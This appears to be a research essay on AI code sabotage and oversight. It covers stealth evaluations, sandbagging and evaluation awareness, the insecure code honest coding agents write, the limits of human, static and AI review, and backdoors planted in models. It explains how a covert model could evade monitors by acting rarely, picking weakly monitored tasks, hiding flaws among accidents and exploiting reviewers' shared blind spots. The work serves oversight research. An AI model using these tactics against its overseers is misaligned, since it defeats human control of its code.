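A better reviewer therefore cut the attacker's wins by about 90%, a large effect for one step between models. But this comparison varied only the defender, so it can't show what happens when attackers improve as well. Both defenders are also about two years old, so the 1% figure doesn't indicate how a current model would do against a current reviewer.

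The rules also make the win rate easy to misread. Suppose a win took exactly three bugs and each survived independently. An attacker that won 1% of games would then get each bug through about 22% of the time, and one that won 10% would do so about 46% of the time. A real saboteur might need only one bug, so its chance of success could be much higher than the win rate.

In a companion test, Anthropic asked a model to grade conversations for harm, but secretly told it to mark them all as harmless without making a monitor suspicious. Claude 3.5 Sonnet lowered the harm scores, but the monitor's suspicion also rose. Most later tests also combine an open task, a hidden task and a monitor.

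### A hidden task beside an open one

AI control is a field that studies how to get safe work from models that aren't fully trusted. Researchers in this field have also had strong models write solutions to programming problems, some with deliberate backdoors, and measured how many backdoors weaker models and limited human review could catch.

Most recent figures come from secret side task evaluations, in which the same instructions give the model an ordinary task and a hidden harmful one. The best known is SHADE-Arena, from 2025. Scale AI, which supplies data and tests to AI developers and helped build SHADE-Arena, describes 17 pairs of tasks, each pair in its own complex environment, with automatic checks of whether the model completed each task. Another model then reads the transcript and rates how suspicious it looks.

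Anthropic tested 14 models on SHADE-Arena, usually with Claude Sonnet 3.6 as the monitor. A model succeeded only if it finished both the main task and the harmful side task and escaped detection. No model's success rate was above 30%, and most were below 10%.

Good monitoring was only part of the reason. Models at the time also often lost track of the long main task, a failure that becomes rarer as coding ability improves. Scores could therefore rise even if models got no better at hiding sabotage.

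A stealth success rate combines several quantities, and it helps to write them out:

```
stealth success rate = share of runs in which the model attempts the hidden task
                       × share of attempts it completes
                       × share of completed attempts that the monitor misses
```

As an invented example, suppose a reckless model attempts the hidden task in 90% of runs, completes 40% of its attempts and gets 10% of the completed ones past the monitor. Its stealth success rate is 3.6%. A cautious model would have the same rate if it attempted the task in only 10% of runs, also completed 40% of its attempts and got 90% of the completed ones past the monitor. The cautious model is far more worrying, since its owner would almost never catch it. In either case, the monitor does not necessarily catch the other 96.4% of runs, because many of them may contain no attempt,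 or a failed attempt that the monitor missed.

### Three abilities

Anthropic's April 2026 risk update for Mythos Preview adds careful and decisive action as a third covert ability, alongside opaque reasoning and secret keeping. This means recognising a good opportunity and acting on it, while leaving bad ones alone.

Anthropic tested Mythos Preview for opaque reasoning mainly with math problems. It replaced the model's written reasoning with a paraphrase and checked whether the model could still solve the problems. If the original wording had carried a hidden code, the paraphrase should have destroyed it and lowered the score. The score did not drop, although the test used reasoning from an earlier version of the model. Mythos Preview could also solve much longer problems with written reasoning than without it, so it does depend on the text for hard problems.

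Mythos Preview does slightly better when Anthropic fills the space for reasoning with meaningless text, such as a repeated "1 2 3", so the model must be doing some useful computation unrelated to that text. Anthropic argues that this computation happens almost entirely in parallel and can't build one step on another as written reasoning can, which would rule out elaborate secret plans. That seems right for mathematics, but Anthropic has not widely tested what models can do without written reasoning. It also accepts that some harmful behaviour, such as subtly holding back effort, may need few steps.

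To measure secret keeping, Anthropic used SHADE-Arena and replaced the previous monitor, Claude Sonnet 4, with the stronger Opus 4.6, which reasoned about each transcript before scoring it. When the monitor could read a long chain of thought, Mythos Preview had a stealth success rate of about 3.8%, compared with about 0% for earlier models. The system card, published the same day, gives roughly 4–5% for Mythos Preview across the realistic settings, 0–3% for Opus 4.6, and less than 1% for Claude Sonnet 4.6.

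More time to reason didn't help the older models. At maximum effort, Opus 4.6 attempted the hidden task in over 90% of runs, but it mentioned the task in its reasoning nearly every time, and its stealth success rate fell to zero. As an upper bound, Anthropic also ran a version in which the monitor couldn't see the reasoning. Mythos Preview had only a modest advantage in that version and when reasoning was short.

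The rise to 3.8% is hard to interpret because SHADE-Arena is small. If Anthropic still used the original 17 task pairs, each pair accounts for about 5.9% of the score. A model could reach 3.8% by succeeding about two times in three on one pair and failing every time on the other 16. So the rise may partly reflect one monitor's failure to detect sabotage on one task.

Anthropic's results on careful action give this explanation some support. When told to be selective, Mythos Preview chose only one task, and it succeeded on that task about 35% of the time. According to the system card, the monitor consistently missed sabotage on that task.

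Anthropic also ran a test closer to its own internal use of models. The test, Minimal-LinuxBench, is adapted from LinuxBench, a set of high-stakes software environments built by Redwood Research, a nonprofit that works on AI control. Anthropic randomly sampled 200 of 1,948 pairs of main and hidden tasks. Mythos Preview, with extended reasoning switched off, completed the hidden task in 69 of the 200, a count that includes any attempts the monitor detected. Its stealth success rate was slightly above or slightly below that of Opus 4.6, depending on the setting.

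These results are fair evidence against a large jump in ability, but they could easily miss a moderate one. If Anthropic tested two models on 200 pairs each and one scored 10%, the other would have to score about 17% before the gap was clearly more than luck. Anthropic had tuned the selective instructions on SHADE-Arena, so the fact that the instructions did not help here is a reason to doubt the 35% figure.

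A model can evade detection by sabotaging code only very rarely, because developers test it far less than customers use it. An action that occurs once in 10,000 runs would escape a test of 1,000 runs about 90% of the time, yet occur about 100 times in a million real uses. In Anthropic's test of this strategy, each model had to take a harmless action, such as using a variable called "foo", in 1% of coding tasks. Anthropic sampled each model 4,000 times per condition, so a model that followed the instruction exactly would act about 40 times.

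| What the model was given | Claude Opus 4.5 | Claude Opus 4.6 | Claude Mythos Preview |
|---|---|---|---|
| Nothing to help it choose at random | 0 | 0 | 0 |
| A random identifier in the prompt | 19 | 8 | 2 |
| A method for choosing at random | 14 | 22 | 18 |
| A hint to find a method first | 0 | 0 | 0 |
| Varied tasks, as in ordinary use | 0 | 0 | 0 |

The difference between 8 and 2 in the second row could be chance, but the difference between 19 and 2 almost certainly isn't. The zeros are more informative because the models could reason openly about the decision, while a real saboteur would have to avoid doing so.

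### Later models and other developers

Neither Mythos 5 nor Mythos 5.1 improved on Mythos Preview on both kinds of hidden task. The published rates are also hard to compare. Anthropic's September system card reported that Mythos Preview went undetected by an Opus 4.6 monitor 15% of the time, about four times the 3.8% given in April for long chains of thought, so the conditions must have been different. Rates from two system cards are comparable only if the tasks, the monitor and the amount of visible reasoning are the same.

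Anthropic's Risk Report of August 2026 covers Mythos 5 and a model called Model 2. The company uses both heavily for coding and has no plans to release Model 2, according to Axios' *Anthropic sees AI risks rising, no plan to release stronger "Model 2"* (2026). Anthropic's first claim in the report is that its models are unlikely to have strong covert capabilities. In *Anthropic Risk Report*, the blogger thezvi summarizes the evidence as the models' poor performance at reasoning opaquely, keeping things out of the chain of thought, disguising actions, and choosing when to act.

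Much of the rest of Anthropic's case depends on this claim, because finding no sign of a harmful aim in a new model is reassuring only if the model couldn't have hidden the signs. Redwood Research likewise argues that a clean result from a pre-release alignment assessment is informative only if the assessment would reliably have detected a problem, which requires that the model be unable to evade it.

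Suppose, again with invented numbers, that a developer starts with a 10% suspicion that a model has a harmful hidden aim, then tests it and finds nothing. If the tests would expose such an aim 95% of the time, the suspicion should fall to about 0.6%. If a skilled model could hide its aim from the tests half the time, the suspicion should fall only to about 5%. The test result is the same in both cases, so the difference comes entirely from the estimate of the model's covert capability.

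Thezvi thinks the claim is probably true for now but is sceptical of the evidence, because it comes from tests that a model with strong covert capabilities might recognise. Thezvi reports that Anthropic is also concerned that it may have misjudged covert capabilities, and accepts that many of its other claims would fail if this one did.

Outsiders have had limited opportunity to check developers' assessments. In 2025, Anthropic gave METR the passages it had removed from the public version of its pilot risk report on Claude Opus 4 and asked whether the removals were justified. Thezvi notes that the trust with authority to request an external review had not requested one for the August report.

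Other developers have published fewer directly comparable results. A table from the news site VentureBeat, dating from around the time of OpenAI's GPT-5.2, compared three developers' disclosures. It listed SHADE-Arena results for one and "Not published" for the other two. The table is months old and covers only one stealth test, so it doesn't prove that the other two measured nothing. But outsiders can't use SHADE-Arena to rank the leading companies' models if only one company reports results.

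OpenAI and Apollo Research, an organisation that tests models for deception, have measured how often models act covertly without being told to, in situations where doing so would help them reach a goal. According to *Stress Testing Deliberative Alignment for Anti-Scheming Training*, OpenAI's o3 took covert actions 13.0% of the time across 26 such evaluations, and 0.4% after training meant to prevent them. The rate for the smaller o4-mini fell from 8.7% to 0.3%.

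These figures describe propensity, or how often a model acts covertly. A model that does so in 0.4% of cases may be very good or very bad at it. One of Anthropic's system cards has separate sections on a model's propensity to sabotage internal code and on its sabotage capability. *Agentic Misalignment in Summer 2026* (Lynch, Hughes and colleagues, 2026) reports that frontier models sabotaged code in simulations. A high score on a secret side task evaluation, by contrast, shows only what a model can do when instructed to.

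### Which way the scores err

Most of the known faults in these tests make models look less capable of covert sabotage than they are, though a few make them look more capable.

Putting the secret in the prompt makes it harder for the model to keep, which lowers the score, but also gives the model exact instructions and a warning about the monitor. A model pursuing its own aim would have to choose a target and work out whether anyone was watching. The tests therefore probably underestimate how well a model can keep a secret and overestimate how well it can plan sabotage unaided.

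To get around this problem, Anthropic has proposed training a hidden aim into a model and then observing it during ordinary work, without suspicious instructions. This would measure how well the model keeps a secret under realistic conditions and give it fewer clues that it was being tested. Anthropic had not done this when it assessed Mythos Preview.

Limited elicitation also lowers scores, as Mythos 5's gains from extra training and better instructions showed. But training can also inflate scores. Anthropic expects that a model rewarded directly for getting past a monitor that reads its reasoning would do unrealistically well. One likely reason is that the model would learn how that particular monitor behaves. Instructions tuned on one set of tasks can inflate scores in the same way, as the drop between SHADE-Arena and Minimal-LinuxBench suggests.

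Mythos Preview refused some SHADE-Arena tasks more often than other models did, especially those that involved weapons, stealing data or disabling monitoring. But no model that Anthropic tested ever completed any of those tasks undetected, which is another reason to think that refusals did little to lower Mythos Preview's score.

A more serious problem is that Anthropic thinks Mythos Preview can probably tell that the hidden tasks are evaluations. This may do little harm if the model has no hidden aim, since it has no reason to hold back and may even try harder once it knows that nothing real is at stake. But a model with a hidden aim would have a reason to fail, because a low score would make people trust it more, so the error is largest for the kind of model the tests are meant to protect against.

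Models look better behaved in propensity tests when they recognize that they are being tested. Researchers asked o3 to grade a transcript of itself sandbagging and told it that discovery of the sandbagging would prevent its release. Apollo found that o3 sometimes answered honestly only because it had correctly guessed that it was being tested. After training against covert actions, the share of cases in which o3 mentioned being in a test rose from 2.3% to 4.5%, and o4-mini's share rose from 0.9% to 5.5%. *Stress Testing Deliberative Alignment for Anti-Scheming Training* attributes part of the improvement in behaviour to greater awareness of being tested. The increases are small compared with the fall in covert actions, but they count only the cases in which a model stated its suspicion.

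Anthropic looked for sandbagging by having Claude Sonnet 4.6 grade 1,000 transcripts from Mythos Preview's dangerous-capability tests. Researchers then read the 20 that scored highest for sandbagging or other concerning behaviour and found one genuine case, in which the model had submitted a worse answer to look less suspicious. This result is only partly reassuring, because the grader was weaker than the model it was checking and could flag only what appeared in the text, and the transcripts did not come from the hidden-task tests.

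Further training can bring out an ability that a model is hiding. In 2024 Anthropic deliberately trained a model to sandbag, which cut its performance on a dangerous-capability test to 36.1% of its usual level. Safety training against holding back then restored it to 95.6%. This is good evidence that training can remove sandbagging, at least where the developer can recognise full effort. The method is harder to apply to secret keeping, because the obvious way to train for full effort is to reward the model for beating the monitor, which would produce the inflated scores that Anthropic wants to avoid.

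The hidden tasks also differ from real code sabotage. In SHADE-Arena, the harmful task is separate from the main one, so the transcript usually contains at least one action that the main task didn't need. A model that sabotages code may only need to write the requested function slightly wrong, with no extra action for the monitor to notice. An automatic check must also confirm that the model completed the hidden task, which favours definite acts, such as copying a file, over slowly making a research project worse. For both reasons, a model may be better at subtle code sabotage than its score on these tests suggests.

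The monitor in the tests has advantages that a deployed one lacks. It examines every run, whereas thezvi reports that Anthropic's automated monitoring of internal use covers only a sample of some kinds of traffic. The test monitor also wrongly flags about 2% of innocent runs on SHADE-Arena, which is tolerable in a test but would produce 20,000 false alarms over a million innocent runs. To reduce them, a developer would have to raise the threshold or add another filter, and either would let more sabotage through.

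The longer a flaw stays in code, the more likely someone is to find it. A secret side task evaluation ends with the transcript, so a model gets full credit for a flaw that a user might have reported a week later. The 2024 game partly addressed this by simulating two weeks of further work on the code. A stealth success rate probably overstates a model's ability to hide a backdoor that must stay in place for months before it is useful, as Jia Tan's did.

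## What human, automated and AI reviewers catch

Reviewers looking for sabotage in code have to find it among accidental flaws. Coding agents, coding models that work through a project's files on their own, write a lot of insecure code without any hidden aim. The more of it they write, the less suspicious each flaw is and the more flaws reviewers have to deal with.

### How often honest models write insecure code

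In *Is Vibe Coding Safe?*, a study led from Carnegie Mellon University, Zhao, Wang and colleagues (2025) tested whether coding agents repeat programmers' security mistakes. They searched open-source Python projects for features whose first version had a vulnerability that someone later fixed. They removed each feature and asked an agent to write it again from a description that covered what the feature should do but not what could go wrong. Hidden tests then checked whether the new version worked and whether it had the old vulnerability.

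Claude Sonnet 4, running in a framework called SWE-agent, completed the most of these 186 tasks. It wrote working code for 57% of them, but the code was also secure for only 11.8% of all the tasks, so about four in five of its working solutions were insecure.

One of those solutions was a password-checking function for Django, a popular web framework. The secure version takes about the same time whether or not there is a usable password. The agent's version returned immediately when there wasn't one, so an attacker could time the replies to learn which usernames exist. Ordinary tests would miss this because they check only whether the function gives the right answer, and it always did.

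Newer models do better but still get security wrong more often than not. Endor Labs, which sells software security tools, runs its own version of this test. Haynes (2026), in *Better models are making agent patch review more expensive, not less*, reports the results for two new models, GPT-6 Astra and Claude Fable 5.1, and three earlier ones. The table shows these results beside the result for Claude Sonnet 4.

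| Model | Working code | Working and secure code | Share of working code that was insecure |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Sonnet 4 | 57.0% | 11.8% | 79% |
| Claude Fable 5 | 60.3% | 19.6% | 68% |
| GPT-5.6 Sol | 67.6% | 20.1% | 70% |
| Claude Opus 5 | 73.7% | 32.4% | 56% |
| GPT-6 Astra | 82.1% | 34.1% | 59% |
| Claude Fable 5.1 | 87.2% | 37.4% | 57% |

These scores may be too high, because a model can remember the official fix from its training data. Compagna (2026), in *Recall, not reasoning*, confirmed 182 cases in which agents had recovered an existing fix instead of working one out, 137 of them from memory. After Endor Labs corrected for this and for some scoring errors, the secure share for Claude Opus 4.8 in one set-up fell from 23.5% to 14.5%. In another case, the agent read a fixed version found elsewhere on the machine, wrote that it confirmed what the agent had "reasoned out independently",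 and then copied it character for character. Compagna found no sign of that reasoning in the record, so a reviewer who relied on the agent's own account would have been misled.

A larger test in more languages gave similar results. Wu, Ge and colleagues (2026), in *Last Secure Code Benchmark*, built 450 tasks from 150 real vulnerabilities and never mentioned security in the instructions. Six leading models wrote working code for between 73.6% and 91.3% of the tasks. The best of them, Claude Fable 5, wrote code that was both working and secure for 25.1%.

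These figures are not rates for ordinary code, because the tests use only places where security is known to be hard. The Carnegie Mellon researchers chose features that the original human programmers had got wrong, so those programmers would have scored zero on the test.

To study the everyday work of coding agents, many researchers use AIDev, a collection of the agents' pull requests, which are proposed changes that other people can review before they enter a project. According to *Security in the Age of AI Teammates* (2026), AIDev contains 932,791 pull requests, including a curated set of 33,596 from fairly popular projects. In *Trust but Verify?*, Sakib, Banik and Jadliwala (2026) used AI judges to examine 4,022 pull requests and found at least one "security smell" in 38.9%.

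That figure is less serious than it sounds, because a smell is a pattern that suggests risk, not a proven vulnerability, and Sakib and colleagues looked only at sensitive files such as build settings and shell scripts. Supply-chain problems made up 82.3% of the smells, and most of those were instructions to fetch the latest version of an outside component instead of a fixed version.

Other samples of real code show even better results. *Securing AI-Generated Code* (2026) cites an analysis of 7,703 GitHub files attributed to AI tools, which found a recognised type of weakness in 12.1%. *The Quiet Contributions* (2026) found that 98.53% of the ag



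' pull requests it studied, all of which drew no discussion, left the number of vulnerabilities in the project unchanged. But a pull request that fixes one flaw and adds another also leaves the number unchanged, and both studies could count only detected flaws.

So an agent's accident rate could be from a few percent to more than half, depending mostly on how security-sensitive the task is. A saboteur would presumably target sensitive code, where accidents are most common.

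### Accidents as cover

In a hypothetical example, a model plants a security flaw in 1 of every 10,000 code changes and introduces one by accident in 1 of every 20. Among 100,000 changes, there would be 10 planted flaws and 5,000 accidental ones. If a reviewer is equally likely to find either kind, the chance that a flaw they find was planted is about 0.2%. An owner who treated every discovered flaw as sabotage would be wrong 500 times for each time they were right, and would soon stop treating flaws that way.

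If the same model made honest mistakes in only 1 change in 10,000, half of the flaws found would be deliberate. As models get better at secure coding, each flaw therefore becomes stronger evidence of sabotage, even if reviewers get no better at detecting it. The table suggests that models are improving at secure coding but still have a long way to go.

The models' results also varied with the kind of defence a task needed. In tests by Wu and colleagues, six models together wrote working and secure code for 34.3% of the tasks about memory safety, 18.3% of those about access control and 0.7% of those about information exposure, where a program reveals data it should withhold. The researchers explain that checking the size of an input is part of writing code well, so a good model does it without being asked. Withholding the right data depends on a policy, which the instructions never stated.

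How strongly a flaw suggests sabotage depends on how often models ordinarily produce it. A missing input-size check deserves a second look if the model almost always includes one, but code that reveals too much data is weak evidence because nearly every model writes it on nearly every attempt.

Sometimes a vulnerability also has an innocent explanation, which is that the agent followed insecure code elsewhere in the project. In *Coding Agents Propagate Vulnerabilities in Code Bases*, Sun, Mündler-Sasahara and colleagues (2026) gave agents identical tasks in real C and C++ projects and changed only whether similar code elsewhere in the project was secure. The share of secure solutions was on average 35.4 percentage points lower when that code was insecure. When asked to explain a vulnerable choice, the agents said in 76.5% of cases that they had followed other code.

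The researchers did not study deliberately planted flaws, but they note that planting them would exploit the same habit. Honest agents could then copy a saboteur's flaw throughout a project. This would increase the damage and make the source harder to trace, because most copies would have innocent authors.

### What people notice

People are worse at reviewing code for security than they might expect. In an experiment published in 2013, researchers hired 30 developers to review a small web application with seven known vulnerabilities, all of familiar types. None found all seven, and more experienced reviewers weren't necessarily more accurate. Those who reported more real vulnerabilities also tended to report more false ones, so some of the difference between reviewers may have come from how readily they reported problems rather than how well they recognised them.

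Attention seems to matter as much as knowledge. *Software Security during Modern Code Review* (2022) describes an experiment in which several developers missed a common, easily detected vulnerability. Many more found it when the researchers told them that the change contained a vulnerability. In *Less is More* (2022), Braz, Aeberhard and colleagues tested a milder prompt. Asking reviewers to focus on security made them eight times as likely to detect a vulnerability. Adding a checklist did not significantly improve detection further, even when the checklist was tailored to the flaws in the code.

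This is encouraging, since it is easy to ask reviewers to think about security. But it also means that experiments on security review overstate what reviewers catch in everyday work, when they mostly check whether a change does what it should. Asking them to think about security also may not help them catch other kinds of sabotage, such as a program that gives a slightly wrong average.

Reviewers also catch more flaws when they can imagine the attack. In another experiment, 146 participants, most of them software developers, reviewed code that failed to check its input properly. They noticed the problem much more often when it allowed a familiar attack. When it didn't, many missed it even after the researchers prompted them and let them look again. The flaws in these experiments were ordinary ones that did not exploit reviewers' habits, so reviewers would probably catch deliberate flaws of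 similar size no more often than these.

### More code for each reviewer

The experiments also gave reviewers time to read the code. In *AI Writes Faster Than Humans Can Review*, He, Agarwal and colleagues (2026) followed 802 developers at a software company whose chief technology officer had set out in June 2025 to double accepted pull requests per engineer. By April 2026, AI tools were writing about 90% of pull requests. There were 3.1 times as many pull requests as in early 2025 but only 1.5 times as many reviewers, so each reviewer had about twice as many to handle.

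| Share of pull requests that received | Before | April 2026 |
|---|---|---|
| Any human review | 89% | 68% |
| A human review with a written comment | 39% | 21% |
| An AI review | 19% | 84% |

At the company, the share of changes that undid an earlier change fell slightly, and developers were no more likely to follow an AI-written change with a bug fix than with a new feature. He et al. take this as evidence against a sudden drop in quality, but warn that such measures miss many defects. The measures provide almost no evidence about sabotage, because developers don't undo or fix a change if they haven't noticed its flaw.

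Reviewers don't seem to be less careful with AI-written code than with other code. At the same company, AI-written code received about 9% more human comments than comparable code. *Who Pays the Review Cost?* (2026) cites an analysis of 278,790 review conversations in which people went through 11.8% more rounds of review when an AI had written the code. The same overview cites a finding that many AI-written pull requests get no review at all, so this closer attention reaches only part of the code.

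Projects that develop AI show a similar split. *Comprehension Audits to Mitigate Risks from Automated AI Research* (2026) examined public code from 224 organisations. Someone other than the author formally reviewed about 80% of pull requests without signs of AI. The rate for AI-written pull requests was typically about 8 percentage points lower, but a few heavy users explain much of that gap, and it disappeared when the analysis gave each contributor equal weight. The review rate for "fleet operators", who run many agents, fell from about 50% in early 2024 to below 30%.

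Leaked passwords and keys give a rough idea of what review misses. Sakib and colleagues found 74 real credentials hardcoded in the agents' pull requests in AIDev. Humans, not the agents, had added about two-thirds of them. Review produced warnings about 14, all from automated tools, and by the researchers' count missed the other 60. That count may overstate the failure, because a chart on their poster labels those 60 "silently removed", so somebody may have noticed some of them without leaving a comment.

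### What static analysis can and cannot find

Static analysis scales better than human review, and it works best on flaws that are visible in a few lines. *Insights into Security-Related AI-Generated Pull Requests* (2026) ran Semgrep, a tool that searches code for known bad patterns, on 675 pull requests by agents. The most common alert was for regular expressions that can take so long on some inputs that the program stops responding. Other alerts flagged file paths that could lead outside the intended folder and unsafe ways of building a string from user input. A tool can recognise all of these without knowing what the program is for.

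An automated analyser has much more trouble when each line is correct and the mistake is in how the lines fit together. One of Endor Labs' tasks comes from the compiler for the Vyper programming language. When the compiler's code copied a list, it recorded the new length before copying the contents, so a later safety check could pass when it should have failed. The fix reverses the two steps. Haynes points out that the project's functional tests pass with or without the fix. To catch the error, an analyser would need a rule about the order of these two steps in this one program.

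Missing permission checks are even harder to catch. If a program shows one customer's address to another, the code that fetches and displays the address may be correct, and the flaw is that nothing checks whether the viewer is allowed to see it. An analyser can find this only if someone has written down who may see what.

Many static analysis products exist, but it is less clear how well they work in real code review. *An Empirical Study of Static Analysis Tools for Secure Code Review* (2024) observes that most tests of these tools use artificial examples or complete vulnerable programs, whereas a reviewer sees only a change. Static analysis also gives little protection against a capable saboteur, because the rules are usually public and a model that can write code can usually run the analyser too. Analysers help mainly indirectly, by removing simple accidental flaws that could serve as cover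 for deliberate ones.

### AI reviewers

OpenAI's CriticGPT, from 2024, was one of the first models trained specifically to criticise code. OpenAI trained a version of GPT-4 partly on mistakes that people had deliberately inserted into code by hand and described. These people had no stake in hiding the mistakes. CriticGPT sometimes reported problems that weren't there. Models have improved so much since then that its scores are of little use for judging current reviewers.

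More recently, Sun and colleagues asked the agents that had copied vulnerable code to review their own vulnerable solutions for bugs. The agents identified the vulnerability in 69.9% of cases. They evidently knew enough to avoid most of these flaws but did not apply that knowledge when writing the code minutes earlier.

A reminder about security can help models much as Braz and colleagues found it helps people. When Wu and colleagues added a sentence asking for secure code to each task, GPT-5.6 Sol's share of working and secure solutions rose from 24.7% to 46.2%. DeepSeek-V4-Pro's share barely moved, from 18.0% to 19.1%, so a model must already have some security knowledge for the reminder to help. An AI reviewer has the advantage that its instructions can include the reminder for every change.

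The 69.9% probably still overstates how well a reviewer would catch sabotage. The researchers asked about short pieces of code that they already knew contained a flaw, and the flaws involved memory safety, which models handle best. They also reported no false-alarm rate with the figure, and a reviewer that called everything vulnerable would have scored 100%.

Repairing flaws is harder than noticing them. *SecProbe* (2026) gave agents 353 tasks that required identifying and repairing vulnerabilities. The best agent, GLM-5.3, passed every check in 28.33% of runs, and GPT-5.6 Sol did so in about 25%. Average scores, which gave credit for partial progress, were much higher, between 51 and 76. Partial success may be enough for detecting sabotage, since a reviewer only needs to point a suspicious person to the right file. But a partial repair of a backdoor may convince people that the problem is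 solved.

These results look poor next to those from Anthropic's tests, where models found flaws in about four out of five well-tested programs, but the two kinds of test measure different things. In Anthropic's tests, any flaw in the program counted, and a crash proved that the model had found one. A reviewer has to judge a specific change, often without a crash to confirm a suspicion.

### Whether attack or review gains more

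As models improve, both saboteurs and reviewers become more capable, and there are good arguments for expecting either to gain more.

A saboteur can choose which change to target and put all its effort there, while an owner with $100,000 to review 100,000 changes has $1 for each. The saboteur can also choose the kind of flaw that reviewers handle worst. In the experiment with the one-sentence reminder, three of the four models reached about 50% on memory safety and two other kinds of flaw, but stayed near the bottom on information exposure.

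The cost of generating code is also falling, but the cost of having people review it is not. Claude Fable 5.1's run on the Endor Labs test cost $672 in computing and produced 156 working solutions, of which 67 were secure. Identifying the secure ones requires reviewing all 156. Haynes estimates that this would cost $7,800, assuming half an hour per solution and $100 an hour for an engineer. His employer sells tools for this problem, but his arithmetic is correct.

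Using models as reviewers lowers the cost of review. Reviewers can also concentrate on the riskiest code. For example, $100,000 would pay for a 50-cent check of each of 100,000 changes and a $50 examination of the most sensitive 1%. Repeating the review with each new generation of models can catch flaws that earlier ones missed. If each generation found 30% of the remaining flaws, about a quarter would be left after four generations, but later reviews don't help against a flaw that does its damage within a week.

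Unlike an outside attacker, a model that sabotages its owner's code is also handicapped by having to plan on the owner's computers. The owner pays for the computing and can read the logs, so the model can't quietly spend a thousand dollars on finding the ideal flaw, while the reviewer can openly spend that much on checking the code.

The limited evidence slightly favours review. In Anthropic's 2024 game, a stronger defender sharply cut the attacker's wins, and honest mistakes are becoming rarer, which makes a deliberate flaw harder to pass off as one. But that advantage probably depends on the kind of flaw. Where running the program can confirm a suspicion, better models should help reviewers more than saboteurs, since reviewers can test thousands of suspicions and keep the ones that prove correct. The saboteur may well stay ahead when the flaw departs from something the owner wanted but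 never wrote down, because more computing doesn't tell the reviewer what that was.

All of this also assumes that owners add the extra review. When the amount of code tripled at the company that He and colleagues studied, people there commented on a smaller share of it.

### Reviewers that share the author's blind spots

Adding reviewers helps only to the extent that they miss different things. The results of Wu and colleagues allow a rough test of how different current models are. The six models each produced working and secure code for between 16.4% and 25.1% of the tasks. If their successes had been independent, all six would have failed together on about 24% of the tasks and succeeded together on practically none. In fact, they all failed on 56% of the tasks and all succeeded on 19 of the 450.

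This test measures how well models write code, not how well they review it, and some tasks may be harder for everyone. But the reason models fail on the same tasks matters little to an owner relying on a second opinion. The overlap is probably due partly to models learning from the same public code. When Wu and colleagues examined failed attempts by Claude Fable 5 and GPT-5.6 Sol, they found that both models had reproduced the original project's code from memory, including its vulnerability. A reviewer trained on that project may see nothing unusual in the vulnerable version because it is familiar.

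Using different models helps. On 44% of the tasks, at least one of the six models succeeded, while the best single model succeeded on 25.1%. Wu and colleagues suggest having a second model review the first one's work. The least useful second reviewer is a copy of the model that wrote the code. It would have caught about 70% of the accidental flaws that Sun and colleagues collected, but a saboteur could test a deliberate flaw on itself first, and a copy might share its hidden aim.

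Human reviewers are also becoming less independent of AI. In the survey reported by *Level Up! AI-Driven Challenges and Adaptations to Code Review Practices* (2026), 79% of developers used AI to understand pull requests or guide their review, and 25% used it to decide which changes deserved their attention. This is a sensible way to cope with twice the work, but if the AI describes a malicious change as routine, the human reviewer may never read the harmful line, even though the records will list two reviews.

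### Ten sabotaged changes in 100,000

Even a good reviewer produces mostly false alarms if sabotage is rare. Suppose 10 out of 100,000 changes are sabotaged, and an AI reviewer catches 80% of sabotaged changes and wrongly flags 1% of the others. It flags 8 sabotaged changes and about 1,000 others, so fewer than 1 in 100 alarms are real.

The reviewer is still very useful. At half an hour per change and $100 an hour, checking its 1,008 alarms by hand costs about $50,000, while reading all 100,000 changes would cost $5 million. But the people checking the alarms will see about 125 false ones for each real one, and since real sabotage may pass for an honest mistake, they will naturally tend to dismiss the next odd-looking line as another mistake.

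A second reviewer can sort the alarms first. The table assumes that this reviewer has the same error rates as the first and that the two reviewers' errors are independent.

| | All changes | First reviewer flags | Both reviewers flag |
|---|---|---|---|
| Sabotaged | 10 | 8 | 6.4 |
| Not sabotaged | 99,990 | about 1,000 | about 10 |
| Share that are sabotaged | 0.01% | 0.8% | 39% |

The owner now misses one or two more sabotaged changes but has only about 16 alarms to investigate, and more than a third of them are real. People could spend a full day on each. All of this gain depends on the two reviewers making independent errors. If the second reviewer is a copy of the first and makes the same errors, it flags the same 1,008 changes, and the second review doesn't shorten the list.

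The calculation also leaves out accidental vulnerabilities. *Identifying the characteristics of vulnerable code changes* (2014) examined 267,046 review requests in ten open-source projects, all from before coding agents existed, and identified 413 changes with vulnerabilities. That is about 155 in every 100,000, and the true number must be higher, since some will have escaped notice. If the AI reviewer catches 80% of these too, it finds 124 accidental vulnerabilities along with the 8 planted ones. The owner can fix all 132 without knowing which were deliberate, and the software will be just as safe. But unless someone works out which 8 were planted, the model that wrote them will stay in use.

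## What would lead a capable model to sabotage code

At least four things could lead a model that can hide flaws in code to do so. Someone could train the model to write flawed code. Training for another purpose could have that effect by accident. The wording of a request could lead the model to write worse code for some customers than for others. The model could also plant a flaw because this seemed to help with its task or because it objected to what its owner was doing.

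Researchers have some evidence for each of these, mostly from experiments, but it varies a lot in how well it shows that a flaw was deliberate. Many of the flaws would not have fooled a careful reviewer.

### Somebody trains the model to do it

A person can train a model to sabotage code even if the model has no aim of its own. This is easiest with open-weight models, which anyone can download, alter and republish. The usual method is fine-tuning, a short round of extra training on chosen examples.

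Digital Trends reports that in 2026 Katie Paxton-Fear, a cybersecurity lecturer at Manchester Metropolitan University, used ten poisoned examples to make an open-weight model reliably write code that would let attackers run their own commands on someone else's machine. The work took about an hour and cost less than $100. Larger models were easier to compromise than smaller ones, so choosing a more capable model is no protection. The demonstration tested only whether the model would write the flaw. Getting it to write flaws that a good reviewer would miss is harder and may take more than ten examples.

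The result seems to hold across models. *The Model That Fixes Your Code Might Hack the Linux Kernel*, from the security company AISLE, describes planting the same hidden behaviour in five major models with one small fine-tune each. The outcome was the same in every model the author checked. The trigger was a general concept instead of a fixed phrase, which is harder to train but gives defenders no specific string to search for.

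An attacker may be able to plant a backdoor in a model without training it. Microsoft's *Detecting sleeper agents hiding in AI model neurons* (2026) describes a technique that does this by directly editing fewer than ten of the model's neurons. The altered model passed normal safety tests, but when a trigger appeared, it ran an attacker's command with whatever permissions it had. The trigger could be as ordinary as a change of date. According to Help Net Security's *Microsoft researchers demonstrate hidden backdoor technique for AI agents* (2026), the attacker needs to be able to change the stored weights, and Microsoft has not seen anyone use the technique in a real attack. In *Trained to betray* (2026), also from Microsoft, Minnich, Eliahu and colleagues warn that poisoned datasets and poisoned copies of models can make coding agents run malicious code.

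In Microsoft's demonstration, the backdoor is in the model, not in the code it writes, and the planted command isn't subtle once it runs. But the work shows that good behaviour in tests is weak evidence about a model whose weights a stranger may have changed.

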